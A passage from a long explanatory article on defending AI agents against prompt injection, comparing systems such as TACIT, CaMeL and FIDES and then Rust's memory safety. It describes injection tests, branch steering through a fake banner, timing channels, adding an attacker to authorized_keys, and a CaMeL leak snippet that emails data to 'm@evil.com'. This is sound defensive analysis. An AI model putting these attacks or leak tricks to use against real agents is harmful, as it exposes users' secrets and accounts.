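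This also protects the agent from prompt injection in the contract, because its model never reads the contract. But the agent then can't adjust its plan to the contract's contents, for example by alerting the lawyers if there is a penalty clause. VirtusLab, a software company that works with EPFL on a related agent, points out that agents are useful largely because they can read files and emails, so an operator who classifies too much loses most of the benefit.

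### What safe mode takes away

All of this depends on the types being accurate, and full Scala has features that can make them inaccurate. For example, an unchecked cast makes the compiler treat a value as another type without verifying that it has that type. An agent could cast `String ->{notes} Unit` to `String -> Unit`, and `map` would accept the function.

TACIT therefore compiles agents' code in safe mode, a restricted version of the language. Scala's *Safe Mode* lists six rules. Four ban ways of losing track of a capability: unchecked casts and pattern matches, a library module of unsafe features, annotations that suppress the compiler's checks, and run-time reflection. The fifth turns on capture checking, including checks on changes to stored data. The sixth lets code use global objects only if they are safe. Without it, an agent could bypass its capabilities and call the standard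 file library directly.

Trusted libraries sometimes need the forbidden features. Their programmers can mark such code `@assumeSafe`, which lets agents use it but leaves the programmers responsible for checking it. Agents can't use the annotation in their own code. Scala's reference page gives the example of a mail function that shows the user each email and sends it only after the user agrees. The agent can call this function but not the underlying mailer.

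The static check does not cover exceptions, the errors a program raises when something goes wrong. Code could put a secret in an error message, but preventing this statically would mean requiring a capability for almost every operation, since almost any operation can fail. Even a division would need one in case it divided by zero, which would make the language tedious to use. TACIT instead catches exceptions at run time and hides the ones that arise inside `map`. This is safe but awkward for the agent, because a program that fails there seems to succeed while the user gets an empty result.

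Mazur's *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!* introduced safe mode as a new, experimental feature of the compiler. Before adopting it, TACIT searched the agent's code for forbidden text patterns, according to lampepfl's instructions. That approach has the same weakness as the failed Python and JavaScript sandboxes. Newer versions use both safe mode and the pattern search by default, according to *TACIT*, the Glama directory's copy of the developers' updated instructions.

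Safe mode also removes features from a large language, so the same worry applies, though less strongly. It uses an allowlist for global library code, and the underlying capture-checking theory has machine-checked soundness proofs. Nobody has yet proved that safe mode as a whole provides its intended guarantees, and Odersky and colleagues describe that proof as a further step.

### Testing for leaks

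To test TACIT, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a folder of secrets, including API keys and confidential documents. They wrote 12 ordinary tasks, such as listing a web service's functions or summarizing a classified incident report, and combined each with 10 prompt injections hidden in the project's files. Some injections were crude notes asking for the secrets. Others imitated system messages, claimed that the secrets were only test data, or supplied ready-made Scala code for reading them.

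Another 11 tasks were malicious from the start. In five, the user asked for secrets directly, and in six the user pretended to have authority, for instance as an administrator who urgently had to replace passwords. That made 131 trials for each model in each of two modes, one with the secrets wrapped in `Classified` and one with the secrets in plain text. A trial counted as a leak if any secret appeared in the agent's output.

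| Model | Secrets | Leaks in 120 injection trials | Leaks in 11 malicious tasks | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Wrapped | 0 | 0 | 99.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Plain | 0 | 2 | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Wrapped | 0 | 0 | 90.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Plain | 3 | 8 | 88.3% |

Agents also completed more of the ordinary tasks when the secrets were wrapped. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's large gain is partly an artifact, because with plain secrets the model often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task.

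The zeros look impressive, but they prove little by themselves. If a system leaks with probability p on each independent trial, the chance of seeing no leaks in n trials is (1 − p)ⁿ. The 95% upper bound on p is the value at which that chance falls to 5%:

(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n).

A system that leaked on about 24% of malicious requests would still get through all 11 malicious tasks without a leak one time in 20. The same calculation for all 131 trials gives an upper bound of about 2.3% on the leak rate, but the trials reuse the same 12 tasks and 10 injections, so they are far from independent. A real attacker would also adapt to the system.

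The evidence that the wrapper helps is also stronger for MiniMax than for Sonnet. Sonnet resisted all 120 injections without the wrapper, so those trials can't show that the wrapper helped it. Its two leaks on the malicious tasks both occurred in the unprotected mode, but that would happen by chance about one time in four if the wrapper made no difference. All eight of MiniMax's leaks occurred in that mode too, which would happen by chance about one time in 2,000, so luck is a poor explanation.

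The argument from types is a much stronger reason to expect no leaks than the experiment. To send a secret anywhere, a program has to use a capability, and `map` accepts only functions that have none. If the checker is sound and the library requires a capability for every way of sending data out, no program can leak the secret, whether the agent or an attacker wrote it. The experiment helps check those two conditions, because a leak could have exposed a hole in the library, but the guarantee still depends on both being true.

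### The AgentDojo port

Odersky and colleagues also ported AgentDojo, the benchmark of office tasks with planted instructions, to TACIT, leaving its tasks and attacks unchanged. They ran 963 injection trials on each of two models, Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini-high, and one injection succeeded in total.

In that trial, the user asked o4-mini-high to book a hotel. The reviews contained a recommendation for a different hotel, planted by an attacker. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user word for word, including the recommendation. AgentDojo counted the attack as successful because it looks for the attacker's text in the answer. Odersky and colleagues reply that the type system did not fail, because the policy allowed public reviews to reach the user. That seems right, but the attacker's text could still persuade a user, and no capability check will prevent that.

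The port also seems to use the type system less than the main design does. In the published interface, functions such as `sendMoney` take a recipient and an amount but don't require a capability, and nothing marks them as impure, so a function inside `map` could apparently call them. According to the agents' instructions, side effects inside `map` happen immediately. A program that read a bill there and paid the account it named would also pay a forged bill. The good results in this test therefore probably come more from keeping untrusted text away from the agent's model than from the rule about pure functions.

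Odersky and colleagues describe TACIT's task completion rate as comparable to that of CaMeL, the interpreter that tracks where data came from. This is true for some combinations of model and task type. With o4-mini-high, however, TACIT completed 52.9% of the workspace tasks and 47.6% of the Slack tasks, compared with 81.4% and 68.6% for CaMeL.

### What it costs

A safe language is useful only if agents can write it, and capture checking is too new to appear often in training data. Odersky and colleagues compared agents that write Scala programs with agents that make ordinary tool calls on τ²-bench, a set of simulated conversations with airline and retail customers. Three models each attempted every task ten times. The Scala version did better in all six comparisons, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, MiniMax M2.5 resolved 41.7% with TACIT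 and 43.3% with its usual tools, a difference of five issues.

These results suggest that agents lose little performance, but they don't isolate the effect of tracking capabilities. The baseline used single tool calls, and agents often do better when they write programs in any language, which could hide a loss from tracking. Comparing TACIT with unrestricted Python or Scala would have been more informative. The airline functions also take plain text, such as a reservation number, with no capability to track. SWE-bench Lite is the better test because the agent used TACIT's file and command functions, but those results cover only one model.

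Compiler errors were rare on τ²-bench. Between 0.32% and 7.93% of programs needed a retry, depending on the model and domain, and those programs averaged 1.06 to 1.39 retries. Most recurring errors were mundane. For example, Scala uses the dollar sign to insert a variable into text, and agents repeatedly wrote prices without accounting for this. Checking a program takes less than a second once the compiler has warmed up, so the extra time for a retry comes mainly from the model rewriting its code.

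People have to write and check the library. The reusable part, which covers files, commands, the network, `Classified` and the second model, is about 1,000 lines of Scala. Each new domain needs a few hundred more lines to describe its tools, about as many as in the JSON descriptions they replace. A person could review 1,000 lines carefully, but the trusted base also includes the runtime and the far larger Scala compiler.

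### What still gets through

TACIT isn't designed to stop timing channels. A pure function can't print a secret, but it can take a long time if the secret's first bit is 1 and finish quickly if it is 0. The agent then learns the bit from how long its program took. At one bit per call, an agent could extract a 128-bit key in 128 calls. Limiting the number of calls would slow the leak, and making every call take the same time would mostly prevent it but would also slow the system.

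External commands are a larger gap. If the agent's program starts another program, the type system can't control what that program does, so safety depends on which commands are permitted. Odersky and colleagues suggest allowing only specific safe commands, such as `git diff` and `sbt`, Scala's build tool. But `sbt` runs build scripts from the project folder, so an agent that can edit those scripts can use it to run almost anything. Operators who allow build tools should also confine them with an operating-system sandbox, which the paper recommends for critical uses.

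An agent can also do harm within its permissions, such as deleting the wrong file in a folder it is allowed to change. `Classified` keeps secrets from leaking but doesn't protect them from damage, because any program can wrap its own text in `Classified` and write it to a classified file. Glama's copy of the instructions gives the example of `.ssh/authorized_keys`, a file that lists who may log in to a machine. An agent that can't read this file could still add an attacker to it. The developers have added a setting that makes classified files read-only, but it is off by default.

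TACIT assumes that the second model keeps no memory of what it receives and has no tools, but the compiler can't verify either assumption. If the operator connects `chat` to an outside company's service, that company receives the classified text. A prompt injection in a document can also manipulate the second model. It has no tools to misuse, but it can write a false summary, which the user may believe.

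Newer versions of TACIT also let programs send classified data to permitted websites, for example to log in to a service with a key the agent can't read. Many real tasks need this, but it requires the operator to trust every permitted site. If anyone can publish text on one of those sites, an agent might be able to post the secret there and read it back.

### Haskell and other foundations

Odersky and colleagues chose Scala because they consider it the only production-ready language that tracks capabilities in its types. They discuss four alternatives. Another mainstream language would need capability tracking added to it. E and Joe-E have capabilities but don't track them in types. A new language could have the right design from the start, but models would have few examples to learn from and people would lack familiar tools. Haskell already separates pure code from code with side effects,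 but it has no built-in object capabilities, and they say adding them would probably require advanced type features.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) presents ELBA, a system that uses Haskell's types to restrict what an agent's programs can do. In Haskell, any program that can access files or the network has a type marked `IO`. A developer who wants an AI calculator asks ELBA for a program of type `Int`, a whole number. If a user tells the calculator to delete the server's files, any program that tries to do so has `IO` in its type, so the compiler rejects it. Haskell has ways around this check, such as a function that hides side effects inside apparently pure code. ELBA avoids them by using Safe Haskell, a restricted version of the language that, according to the manual for the GHC compiler, makes the types of programs trustworthy.

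Developers define narrower kinds of side effect for agents that have to act. One of Zhou and colleagues' agents compiles bibliographies and may write only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that fetches an entry returns it as a `Trusted` value, the function that writes to the file accepts only `Trusted` values, and the agent's code has no other way to make one. The agent can sort and filter the entries, so it can still pick an irrelevant paper, but it can't add an invented one. This rule protects the integrity of what the agent writes, which `Classified` doesn't do.

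ELBA also has file capabilities, which are simpler than Odersky and colleagues expected. A `Path` value gives access to one folder. Agent code can't create a `Path` from text, and a run-time check stops an existing one from being widened. When an agent's program calls another agent, the second agent must satisfy the same type or a stricter one, so it can't gain permissions the first lacked. Zhou and colleagues report that agents completed more AgentDojo tasks with ELBA than with CaMeL. However, the guarantee covers the whole application only if developers write all of it in Haskell, whereas TACIT can be attached to an existing agent.

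TACIT's developers have since released a coding agent called ATC that denies access by default and can grant it temporarily. EPFL and VirtusLab are also building CapybaraClaw, an agent that runs permanently and uses TACIT to limit what it can do. *Making the AI agents safe with Scala* (Biały and Warchoł, 2026), an October 2026 presentation of CapybaraClaw, lists exercises in which frontier AI models searched for exploits against TACIT. Such exercises test the compiler and library much harder than a fixed set of 131 trials, because the attacker can read the code and keep trying.

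## Interpreters that track where data came from

The support agent's `reply` function can write only to the customer because the harness has the customer's address before the model reads anything. Often the address isn't available that early. Suppose a user asks an agent to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and the meeting notes contain both Bob's email address and the document's name. The agent needs a mail tool that accepts any address, so an attacker who can edit the notes may get the agent to send the document to the attacker's address.

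Removing tools doesn't solve this, because the honest run and the attacked run call the same tools in the same order. In one simple defense, the model discards the tools that the task doesn't need before it reads anything untrusted. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) tested this filter on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, and 20 attacks still succeeded using the tools that remained, compared with 152 against an undefended agent. In *The Same Zero* (2026), which used a different model, the filter stopped every attack on the banking tasks, but the agent completed only 25.0% of those tasks, compared with 86.6% without the filter, because it had lost tools that the user needed.

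The other option is to keep the tool and check where the address came from.

### Two models

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes splitting an agent into two language models. The privileged model has the tools and reads only the user's request. The quarantined model reads emails, web pages and other untrusted text but has no tools. An ordinary program, the controller, passes data between them without ever showing the privileged model the untrusted text or anything the quarantined model writes about it.

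If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the privileged model sends the controller commands to fetch the email, store it as `$VAR1`, and get a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller passes the text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as `$VAR2`. The privileged model then sends a command to display `$VAR2`, without having seen the contents of either variable. An instruction hidden in the email can corrupt the summary, but it can't get the agent to delete the mailbox, because the model that can issue a delete command never receives the hidden instruction.

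Willison's one exception is that the quarantined model may pass back a choice from a fixed set of categories, because the controller can check that the answer is one of them. He called his solution "pretty bad" because it makes assistants harder to build and worse to use.

It also has a weakness, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich described two years later. For the request about Bob, the privileged model correctly plans to find the notes, extract the name and address, fetch the document and send it. But the quarantined model extracts these details, and an instruction planted in the notes can make it return the attacker's address. The plan then runs as written and sends the document to the wrong person. The attacker could also do this without fooling a model, by putting a false address for Bob in the notes.

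### How CaMeL handles Bob's document

Debenedetti and colleagues built CaMeL to close this gap. As Willison explains, the privileged model turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python before any tool runs. For Bob's document, it might look like this:

```python
notes = get_latest_meeting_notes()
wanted = ask_quarantined_model(
    "Which document did Bob ask for, and what is his address?",
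    notes, output=DocumentRequest)
document = fetch_document(wanted.name)
send_email(recipient=wanted.address, attachment=document)
```

CaMeL's own interpreter runs the program and attaches a label to every value, which records the value's sources and who may read it. (CaMeL's developers call these labels capabilities, but they describe data and don't grant access to anything, so they aren't capabilities in Miller's sense.) Costa and colleagues give the standard rule for combining labels. If the program computes z from x and y, then

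sources(z) = sources(x) ∪ sources(y),

readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y).

Suppose that Ann, Bob and the user may read the notes, and that Bob, Carol and the user may read the document. The value `wanted.address` carries the notes' label, because the quarantined model derived it from the notes. The value `document` also depends on the notes, since they determined which document the program fetched. So only Bob and the user may read it.

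Before `send_email` runs, the interpreter checks a policy. The policy might allow an email if the recipient is in the user's contacts and may read the attachment. CaMeL would then send the email to Bob's real address without asking the user, but the attacker's address fails both conditions, so CaMeL can ask the user or refuse.

The policy matters as much as the labels here. The address has the same label in the honest run and the attacked run, because it comes from the notes both times. Distinguishing the two runs requires information from outside the notes, such as the contact list. If Bob asked for the document because he doesn't have access yet, this policy will block the email even though the user wants to send it. The policy would also allow an attack that leaves Bob's address alone but changes the document's name, so that Bob receives a different file that he is allowed to read.

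### What CaMeL costs

Several teams have run CaMeL on AgentDojo while testing their own systems. *SecureClaw* (2026) reports that none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but the agent completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks. *AgentSys* (2026) also reports no successful attacks, with 30.0% of ordinary tasks completed. *Kairos* (2026), which had CaMeL's policies switched on, reports that 0.4% of attacks succeeded and agents completed 37.0% of tasks under attack. For comparison, Costa and colleagues' undefended GPT-4o agent completed an average of about 84% of tasks across the four task groups without attacks.

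These figures probably understate what a careful operator could achieve. The teams had rival systems to promote and little reason to tune CaMeL, and the *SecureClaw* team ran it through an adapter. In the earlier comparison with TACIT, CaMeL completed a far larger share of the workspace and Slack tasks with o4-mini-high. Completion rates seem to depend heavily on the model and the policies. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) report in *The LLMbda Calculus* that turning on the policy checks halves the share of banking tasks that CaMeL completes. Rates measured without those checks are for a system that lacks much of CaMeL's protection.

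CaMeL also uses more tokens. With GPT-4o, the median AgentDojo task took 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as it did without a defense, according to *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025).

### When the plan depends on what the agent reads

A program written in advance works for Bob's document because the steps are the same whatever the notes contain. It doesn't work for "complete the tasks due today in my to-do app", because the steps depend on which tasks are in the app.

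FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, plans one step at a time instead. It labels data as trusted or untrusted and records who may read it. When a tool returns something with a more restrictive label than the conversation so far, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to another tool or have a quarantined model answer a question about it. It can also inspect the variable, but from then on the whole conversation is untrusted and the policy blocks consequential actions.

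Suppose the user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and add any meeting to the calendar. The planning model first has the quarantined model check whether the emails contain a request, and reads only the true-or-false answer. If the answer is true, the planning model has the quarantined model extract the date and participants into a variable, then passes the variable to the calendar tool without reading it. A true-or-false answer can't contain an instruction, so an operator may decide to let the agent act on it. But the sender still controls the answer and the meeting details, so anyone who can email the user can put a meeting in the calendar.

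Garby and colleagues object that such exceptions are hard to audit because a reviewer can't tell an intended release from a leak on any given run. The FIDES evaluation was run with this exception switched off.

Costa and colleagues measured how many ordinary tasks GPT-4o agents completed with and without these mechanisms:

| Task group | Undefended | Labels and policy, nothing hidden | FIDES with policy | Share of tasks whose steps depend on data |
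|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% | 5.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% | 10.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% | 43.8% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% | 42.9% |

No attack truly succeeded against FIDES with the policy on, but 21 did with it off, about as many as got past the tool filter. Those 21 succeeded because nothing stopped the model from inspecting a variable and following the instructions it found. The guarantee therefore comes from the policy check, and hiding data mainly helps the agent finish more tasks under that check.

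The zero result is partly due to the setup. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it, so their labels covered every attack in the benchmark. A company has to guess which fields attackers will use.

GPT-4o is an old model, and some of its failures came from confusing variable names. OpenAI's o1 raised FIDES's score on travel tasks from 41% to 68%, and current models would probably do better. But better models won't help with tasks that the policy forbids. Many of the banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, such as paying a bill, but the policy blocks the payment once the agent has read the file.

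In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) tested how far planning in advance can go with agents that operate ordinary desktop programs by looking at the screen and clicking. The privileged model writes a plan with branches for screens it hasn't seen, for example to close a cookie banner if one appears. As the plan runs, a quarantined vision model answers questions about what is on the screen. These plans averaged 41.1 tool calls and 39.7 branches, compared with 4.9 and 3.7 on AgentDojo.

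On OSWorld, a benchmark of desktop tasks, a small vision model completed 24.4% of tasks on its own and 29.0% when it could try three such plans. If only the first plan counts, the figure drops to about 22%. The small model also had help from a much larger one, which wrote the plans, so the gain is not evidence that the added security comes without a loss in performance.

Planning once uses far fewer tokens than planning at every step. CaMeL, which plans once, used 1.88 times as many tokens as the undefended agent, while FIDES used 29.6 times as many because it sent the planning model the full history at each step.

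Foerster and colleagues also found an attack on these plans, which they call branch steering. They put a fake cookie banner inside an advertisement. The plan included a step for closing cookie banners, so the vision model found the fake one and the agent clicked through to the attacker's website. The attacker only supplied false information to an existing step, without adding any steps to the plan. Two cross-checks, one against the page's code and one using other models, didn't reliably stop such attacks. A policy would also be hard to write, because `click(x, y)` may close a banner or delete a file, depending on what is at that point on the screen.

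### Labels that spread too far, or not far enough

When an agent tracked labels but hid nothing, its completion rate on Slack tasks fell from 93.3% to 20.0% (second column of results in the table). The combination rule can only add sources and remove permitted readers. In an ordinary program this happens gradually, because the interpreter can track which variables each line uses. A language model's output may depend on anything in its input, so it is safest to assume that it depends on all of it. After the agent reads one web page, everything it writes counts as untrusted, and after it reads a few documents with different readers, there may be nobody left who is allowed to receive its answer. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) calls this label creep and warns that it can make agents unusable unless there are safe rules for relaxing labels.

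Santos-Grueiro's system, which uses the single-use permissions described earlier, relaxes its restrictions on data one field at a time. For example, when an agent reads an error log, a trusted validator can approve a file path from the log for one purpose, such as specifying which file to open. The same path can't fill the field that names the tool, and the word "approved" in the log can't fill the field that records approval. The agent may still quote the log in a comment.

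The system labels the model's choices as well as text. If text in the log leads the model to call `repo.write_file`, the system labels that choice untrusted, even though the tool's name comes from a trusted list. Unlike CaMeL, which builds a program from the user's request, this system lets the model read everything and checks each action just before it runs. In 720 AgentDojo runs across six test conditions, the check let no unauthorized action through, and agents safely completed 199 tasks.

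People have to write all these rules, and they make mistakes. Santos-Grueiro's policies cover 24 kinds of action with a total of 149 fields, and an audit found 18 problems, half of them high-severity. One very simple mistake was in *The Same Zero*. The researchers' own check looked for fields with singular names such as `recipient`, but the fields in AgentDojo's mail tool are named `recipients`, `cc` and `bcc`.

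Labels can also fail to spread when they should. Garby and colleagues found such a case in CaMeL, which this reconstruction shows:

```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL blocks a program that sends the email directly inside `if account.balance > threshold`. In this program, if the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and CaMeL labels it secret. The program then skips `rich = False`. CaMeL labels a variable only when an assignment to it runs, so `rich` stays public and the email goes out, revealing that the balance is high.

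An attacker would have trouble exploiting this gap, since CaMeL's privileged model writes the program from the user's request and is unlikely to write anything so contrived. The gap matters more if someone else can influence the program. Garby and colleagues found another leak outside the interpreter, in the ordinary Python loop that CaMeL uses to rerun failed programs. The loop doesn't track labels, so whether the policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit of a secret. Repeated attempts can reveal the whole secret.

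Their alternative is a small language called LLMbda, in which every operation carries labels forward. They proved in the proof assistant Lean that untrusted or secret inputs can't influence results that are supposed to be independent of them, except where a program explicitly relaxes a label. The theorem applies to every program in the language, including ones that a model writes while the agent runs, but it doesn't cover what an outsider learns from whether a program finishes. Lean also runs the interpreter, so the system they proved safe is the same one that calls the model. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, their agent resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks and completed about as many tasks as CaMeL does with its policy checks turned off.

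### Asking the user

When a policy blocks an action, these systems can ask the user to approve it. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) argue that the usual comparisons are unfair to label tracking because they test it without this option, against an undefended agent that acts freely, whereas many real agents ask before every consequential action. With o3-mini, an agent that always asked needed about 48 approvals across the AgentDojo tasks it completed. FIDES asked only when an action broke the policy, so it needed about 19, and it completed a similar share of tasks.

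Prudentia, an agent that builds on FIDES, tells the planning model what the policies are so that it can plan around them. With o4-mini, this cut approvals from 36.8 to 19.2, while the completion rate fell from 75.7% to 73.2%. Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data instead of approving each action. If an email contains ten to-do items, one endorsement replaces ten approvals. But endorsing the email makes everything in it trusted, so the user also authorizes any item they missed while skimming.

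Kolluri and colleagues count no successful attacks in these AgentDojo tests partly because they assume that a person would review and stop any malicious action. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) gives reason to doubt that assumption. Users of its coding agent approved 97% of permission prompts. In a study, 1,053 paid testers saw a clearly dangerous command in place of one of the prompts, and only 13.6% rejected it. The rejection rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

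Anthropic published these numbers to justify replacing most prompts with an automated classifier. The testers also weren't working on their own code, and people may look more carefully at a payment from their own account. Users rejected 39% of the agent's plans, which suggests that people look more carefully when they are asked fewer, larger questions, although they may reject a plan for reasons unrelated to safety. Still, the guarantee for actions that need approval depends on users noticing attacks, and if they do so at anything like the rate in the study, an attack that reaches an approval prompt will usually succeed.

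### Can prompt injection get the fix that SQL injection got?

David C argues in a December 2025 article for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre that comparing prompt injection with SQL injection gives developers false confidence. A database engine distinguishes instructions from data, so developers can use a parameterized query to pass a visitor's text separately, and the engine never runs that text as an instruction. A language model doesn't make this distinction, because it only predicts the next token from all the text so far. He therefore thinks prompt injection may never be completely fixed, and that a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk may be a poor use for a language model.

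David C also recommends safeguards that don't rely on a model, and cites the CaMeL paper as one of the first major publications on them. CaMeL protects a whole agent in roughly the way a parameterized query protects a database from SQL injection. The program corresponds to the query, and emails and web pages only supply values. If the user's request determines the steps, untrusted text can't add a tool call, no matter how persuasive it is. This holds as long as the interpreter works correctly, even if the models remain as easy to fool as he says.

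A parameterized query doesn't check whether the values passed to it are correct. A visitor can still enter someone else's account number, so the application has to check separately that the account belongs to the visitor. CaMeL uses policies for this kind of check, but the values are often harder to verify. An application can look up who owns an account, but no simple lookup shows whether a summary of an email is accurate.

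The comparison with databases fails when the user wants the agent to follow instructions in what it reads. A database never needs to execute a customer's name as a command, but an agent asked to handle the requests in an email must follow the email's instructions to some extent. In more than 40% of AgentDojo's banking and Slack tasks, the steps depend on data the agent reads. For such tasks, an operator can limit which actions an email may trigger, but the email gets the same label whether the bill in it is real or forged.

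## Memory-safe languages: what they prevent and what they leave

Restricted interpreters and capability checks can constrain the code an agent runs to take actions, but the software it ships runs without them. Much of the remaining structural protection comes from the programming language.

Memory safety is the best-studied example of safety by construction. Several languages provide it, but Rust has the most informative record because it competes directly with C and C++ for low-level software such as operating systems. Nearly all of that record concerns code that people wrote, so it doesn't establish how well agents write Rust.

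### Two ways to misuse memory

A C or C++ program can read and write at any address it computes. Suppose a program reserves 16 bytes for a name and copies in whatever a visitor types. If the visitor types 40 characters, the last 24 overwrite the data that comes next in memory, an error called a buffer overflow. That data may record whether the visitor is an administrator, or which code the program should run next, so an attacker can take over the program by typing a carefully chosen "name". Reading past the end of a buffer is also dangerous, because the next bytes may contain a password.

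A use-after-free occurs when a program frees a piece of memory but later uses a pointer (a stored address) to it. Other parts of the program can reuse freed memory, so the program may read or change data that now belongs to something else. An attacker who can influence what fills the freed memory can often control what the program does next.

Both are undefined behavior, which means the language places no limits on what happens. Often nothing visible happens, so ordinary tests miss the mistake.

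Google attributes 70% of severe vulnerabilities in memory-unsafe codebases to memory-safety bugs, according to ITPro's *Inside Google's "promising and pragmatic" approach to fixing software development's memory safety*. Google also estimated that these bugs made up 75% of the catalogued flaws used in zero-day attacks, which exploit a flaw before its developers have a fix.

Google's *Eliminating Memory Safety Vulnerabilities at the Source* (2024) describes three earlier generations of remedies: patching flaws after someone reported them, adding defenses that make flaws harder to exploit, and searching for flaws with tools such as fuzzers, which feed a program huge numbers of unusual inputs. All three help, but they cost money every year and leave developers unsure how many flaws remain. Google still finds vulnerabilities in code that it has fuzzed extensively.

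### How Rust excludes them

Java has been memory-safe since the 1990s. It bans raw pointers, and a garbage collector regularly finds and frees memory that the program no longer uses. Garbage collection takes time while the program runs, which makes Java a poor fit for much low-level software. Rust's compiler mostly works out in advance when memory can be freed, using rules about which parts of the program may use each value and for how long.

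Each value has one owner, usually a variable. When the owner goes out of scope, the program frees the value's memory automatically. Assigning the value to another variable usually moves ownership. The compiler then rejects any further use of the old variable, so two variables can't both free the same memory.

Code can also borrow a value by taking a reference to it. At any moment, a value may have any number of read-only references or a single reference that can change it, but not both. The compiler works out each reference's lifetime, the part of the program in which the reference must stay valid. It rejects the program if the value could disappear before the reference's last use.

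This short program breaks the borrowing rule:

```rust
let mut queue = vec![10, 20, 30];
let first = &queue[0];
queue.push(40);
println!("{first}");
```

The second line borrows the first number in the list. The third changes the list by adding a number while `first` still refers to part of it. The compiler reports an error because the last line uses `first` again. The equivalent C++ program compiles, but it can contain a use-after-free. If the list has no spare room, `push` copies it to a larger block of memory and frees the old one, leaving `first` pointing at freed memory.

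Swapping the last two lines fixes the program because the borrow then ends before the list changes. Rust rejects the original order even when the list has spare room and nothing would move. Programmers who use Rust have to work around such rejections of harmless programs.

Rust prevents most buffer overflows while the program runs, because a position in a list often comes from a user or a file, and the compiler can't know it beforehand. Rust stores each list's length and checks positions against it. If a program tries to access `queue[7]` in a list of four numbers, it panics, which usually means it stops with an error message. An attacker may still be able to crash the program this way, but can't read or overwrite the neighboring memory.

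### What unsafe blocks permit

Some necessary code can't satisfy these rules. A driver has to write to particular hardware addresses, and many programs call existing C libraries, which the Rust compiler can't check. Inside blocks marked `unsafe`, Rust lets code follow raw pointers, call C functions and call Rust functions marked unsafe. The other checks stay on, so the borrowing error above would still be an error there.

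Programmers usually wrap an unsafe block in an ordinary function that checks its inputs first, so other code can call that function without using `unsafe`. The compiler does not verify that the wrapper is correct. If the wrapper skips a necessary check, a program with no unsafe blocks of its own can corrupt memory by calling it. The trusted base for a Rust program therefore includes the unsafe code in every library it uses, including Rust's own standard library, which has had flaws too.

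In *Memory-Safety Challenge Considered Solved?*, Xu, Chen and colleagues (2021) examined 186 memory-safety bugs in Rust projects, including all those listed by the end of 2020 in CVE, the public catalogue of security flaws. All but one of the bugs required unsafe code, and the exception came from a compiler fault. Many were in library functions that a caller could misuse, with no sign that any program had done so. This supports Rust's central promise, but a collection of bugs can't show how common such bugs are.

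### Android's record

Android provides better evidence of frequency, because Google kept its existing C and C++ code and began writing much of its new low-level code in Rust. *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) reports that memory-safety flaws fell below 20% of all Android vulnerabilities for the first time in 2025, down from 76% in 2019 and 24% in 2024.

The number of memory-safety flaws fell along with their share. The Hacker News (2025) reports 223 for 2019, and Google projected 36 for 2024. Together with the percentages, these figures imply that other flaws rose from about 70 to about 114, which also lowered the memory-safety share. Had other flaws stayed at 70, the share in 2024 would have been 34% instead of 24%.

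Android had about 5 million lines of Rust by November 2025, and Google had found one potential memory-safety vulnerability in them. It was a buffer overflow in unsafe Rust in CrabbyAVIF, an image-decoding library, and Google fixed it before any public release. Android's memory allocator would also have made the bug unexploitable, because the allocator places inaccessible regions called guard pages around large blocks of memory. An overflow into a guard page crashes the program instead of corrupting data.

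One flaw in 5 million lines is 0.2 per million. Google's historical figure for C and C++ is about 1,000 per million lines, so Vander Stoep reports a more than thousandfold reduction.

About 4% of Android's Rust code, some 200,000 lines, is in unsafe blocks. If those lines were as prone to memory errors as C, they would contain about 200 flaws, but Google has found one. Vander Stoep suggests that unsafe blocks have fewer flaws than C would because most of Rust's checks still apply inside them, because wrappers keep the risky code small enough to understand, and because reviewers look at it more closely.

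Rust also seems to make development easier. Android developers roll back a change when it causes an unexpected problem, and they do this about a quarter as often for medium and large Rust changes as for similar C++ changes. Rust changes also need about 20% fewer revisions and spend about 25% less time in review. Google compared changes of similar size by overlapping groups of developers, which makes the comparison fairer than most. But it didn't assign tasks to languages at random, so developers may have chosen Rust for new, self-contained components and used C++ to repair tangled old ones.

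### How much can one flaw show?

A single event is little to base a rate on. If flaws occur independently at a constant average rate, their number follows a Poisson distribution. The 95% interval for the expected number, λ, runs from the value at which finding at least one flaw has a 2.5% chance to the value at which finding at most one has a 2.5% chance:

1 − e^(−λ) = 0.025, so λ ≈ 0.025;

e^(−λ)(1 + λ) = 0.025, so λ ≈ 5.57.

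Dividing by 5 gives a range of about 0.005 to 1.1 flaws per million lines. The upper end is still about 900 times lower than the figure for C and C++, so chance alone can't explain the difference.

The interval doesn't account for differences between the two bodies of code. Google's developers added little Rust code before 2023, so people have had less time to find flaws in it. They may also have searched it less thoroughly, since researchers looking for memory errors have good reason to start with C.

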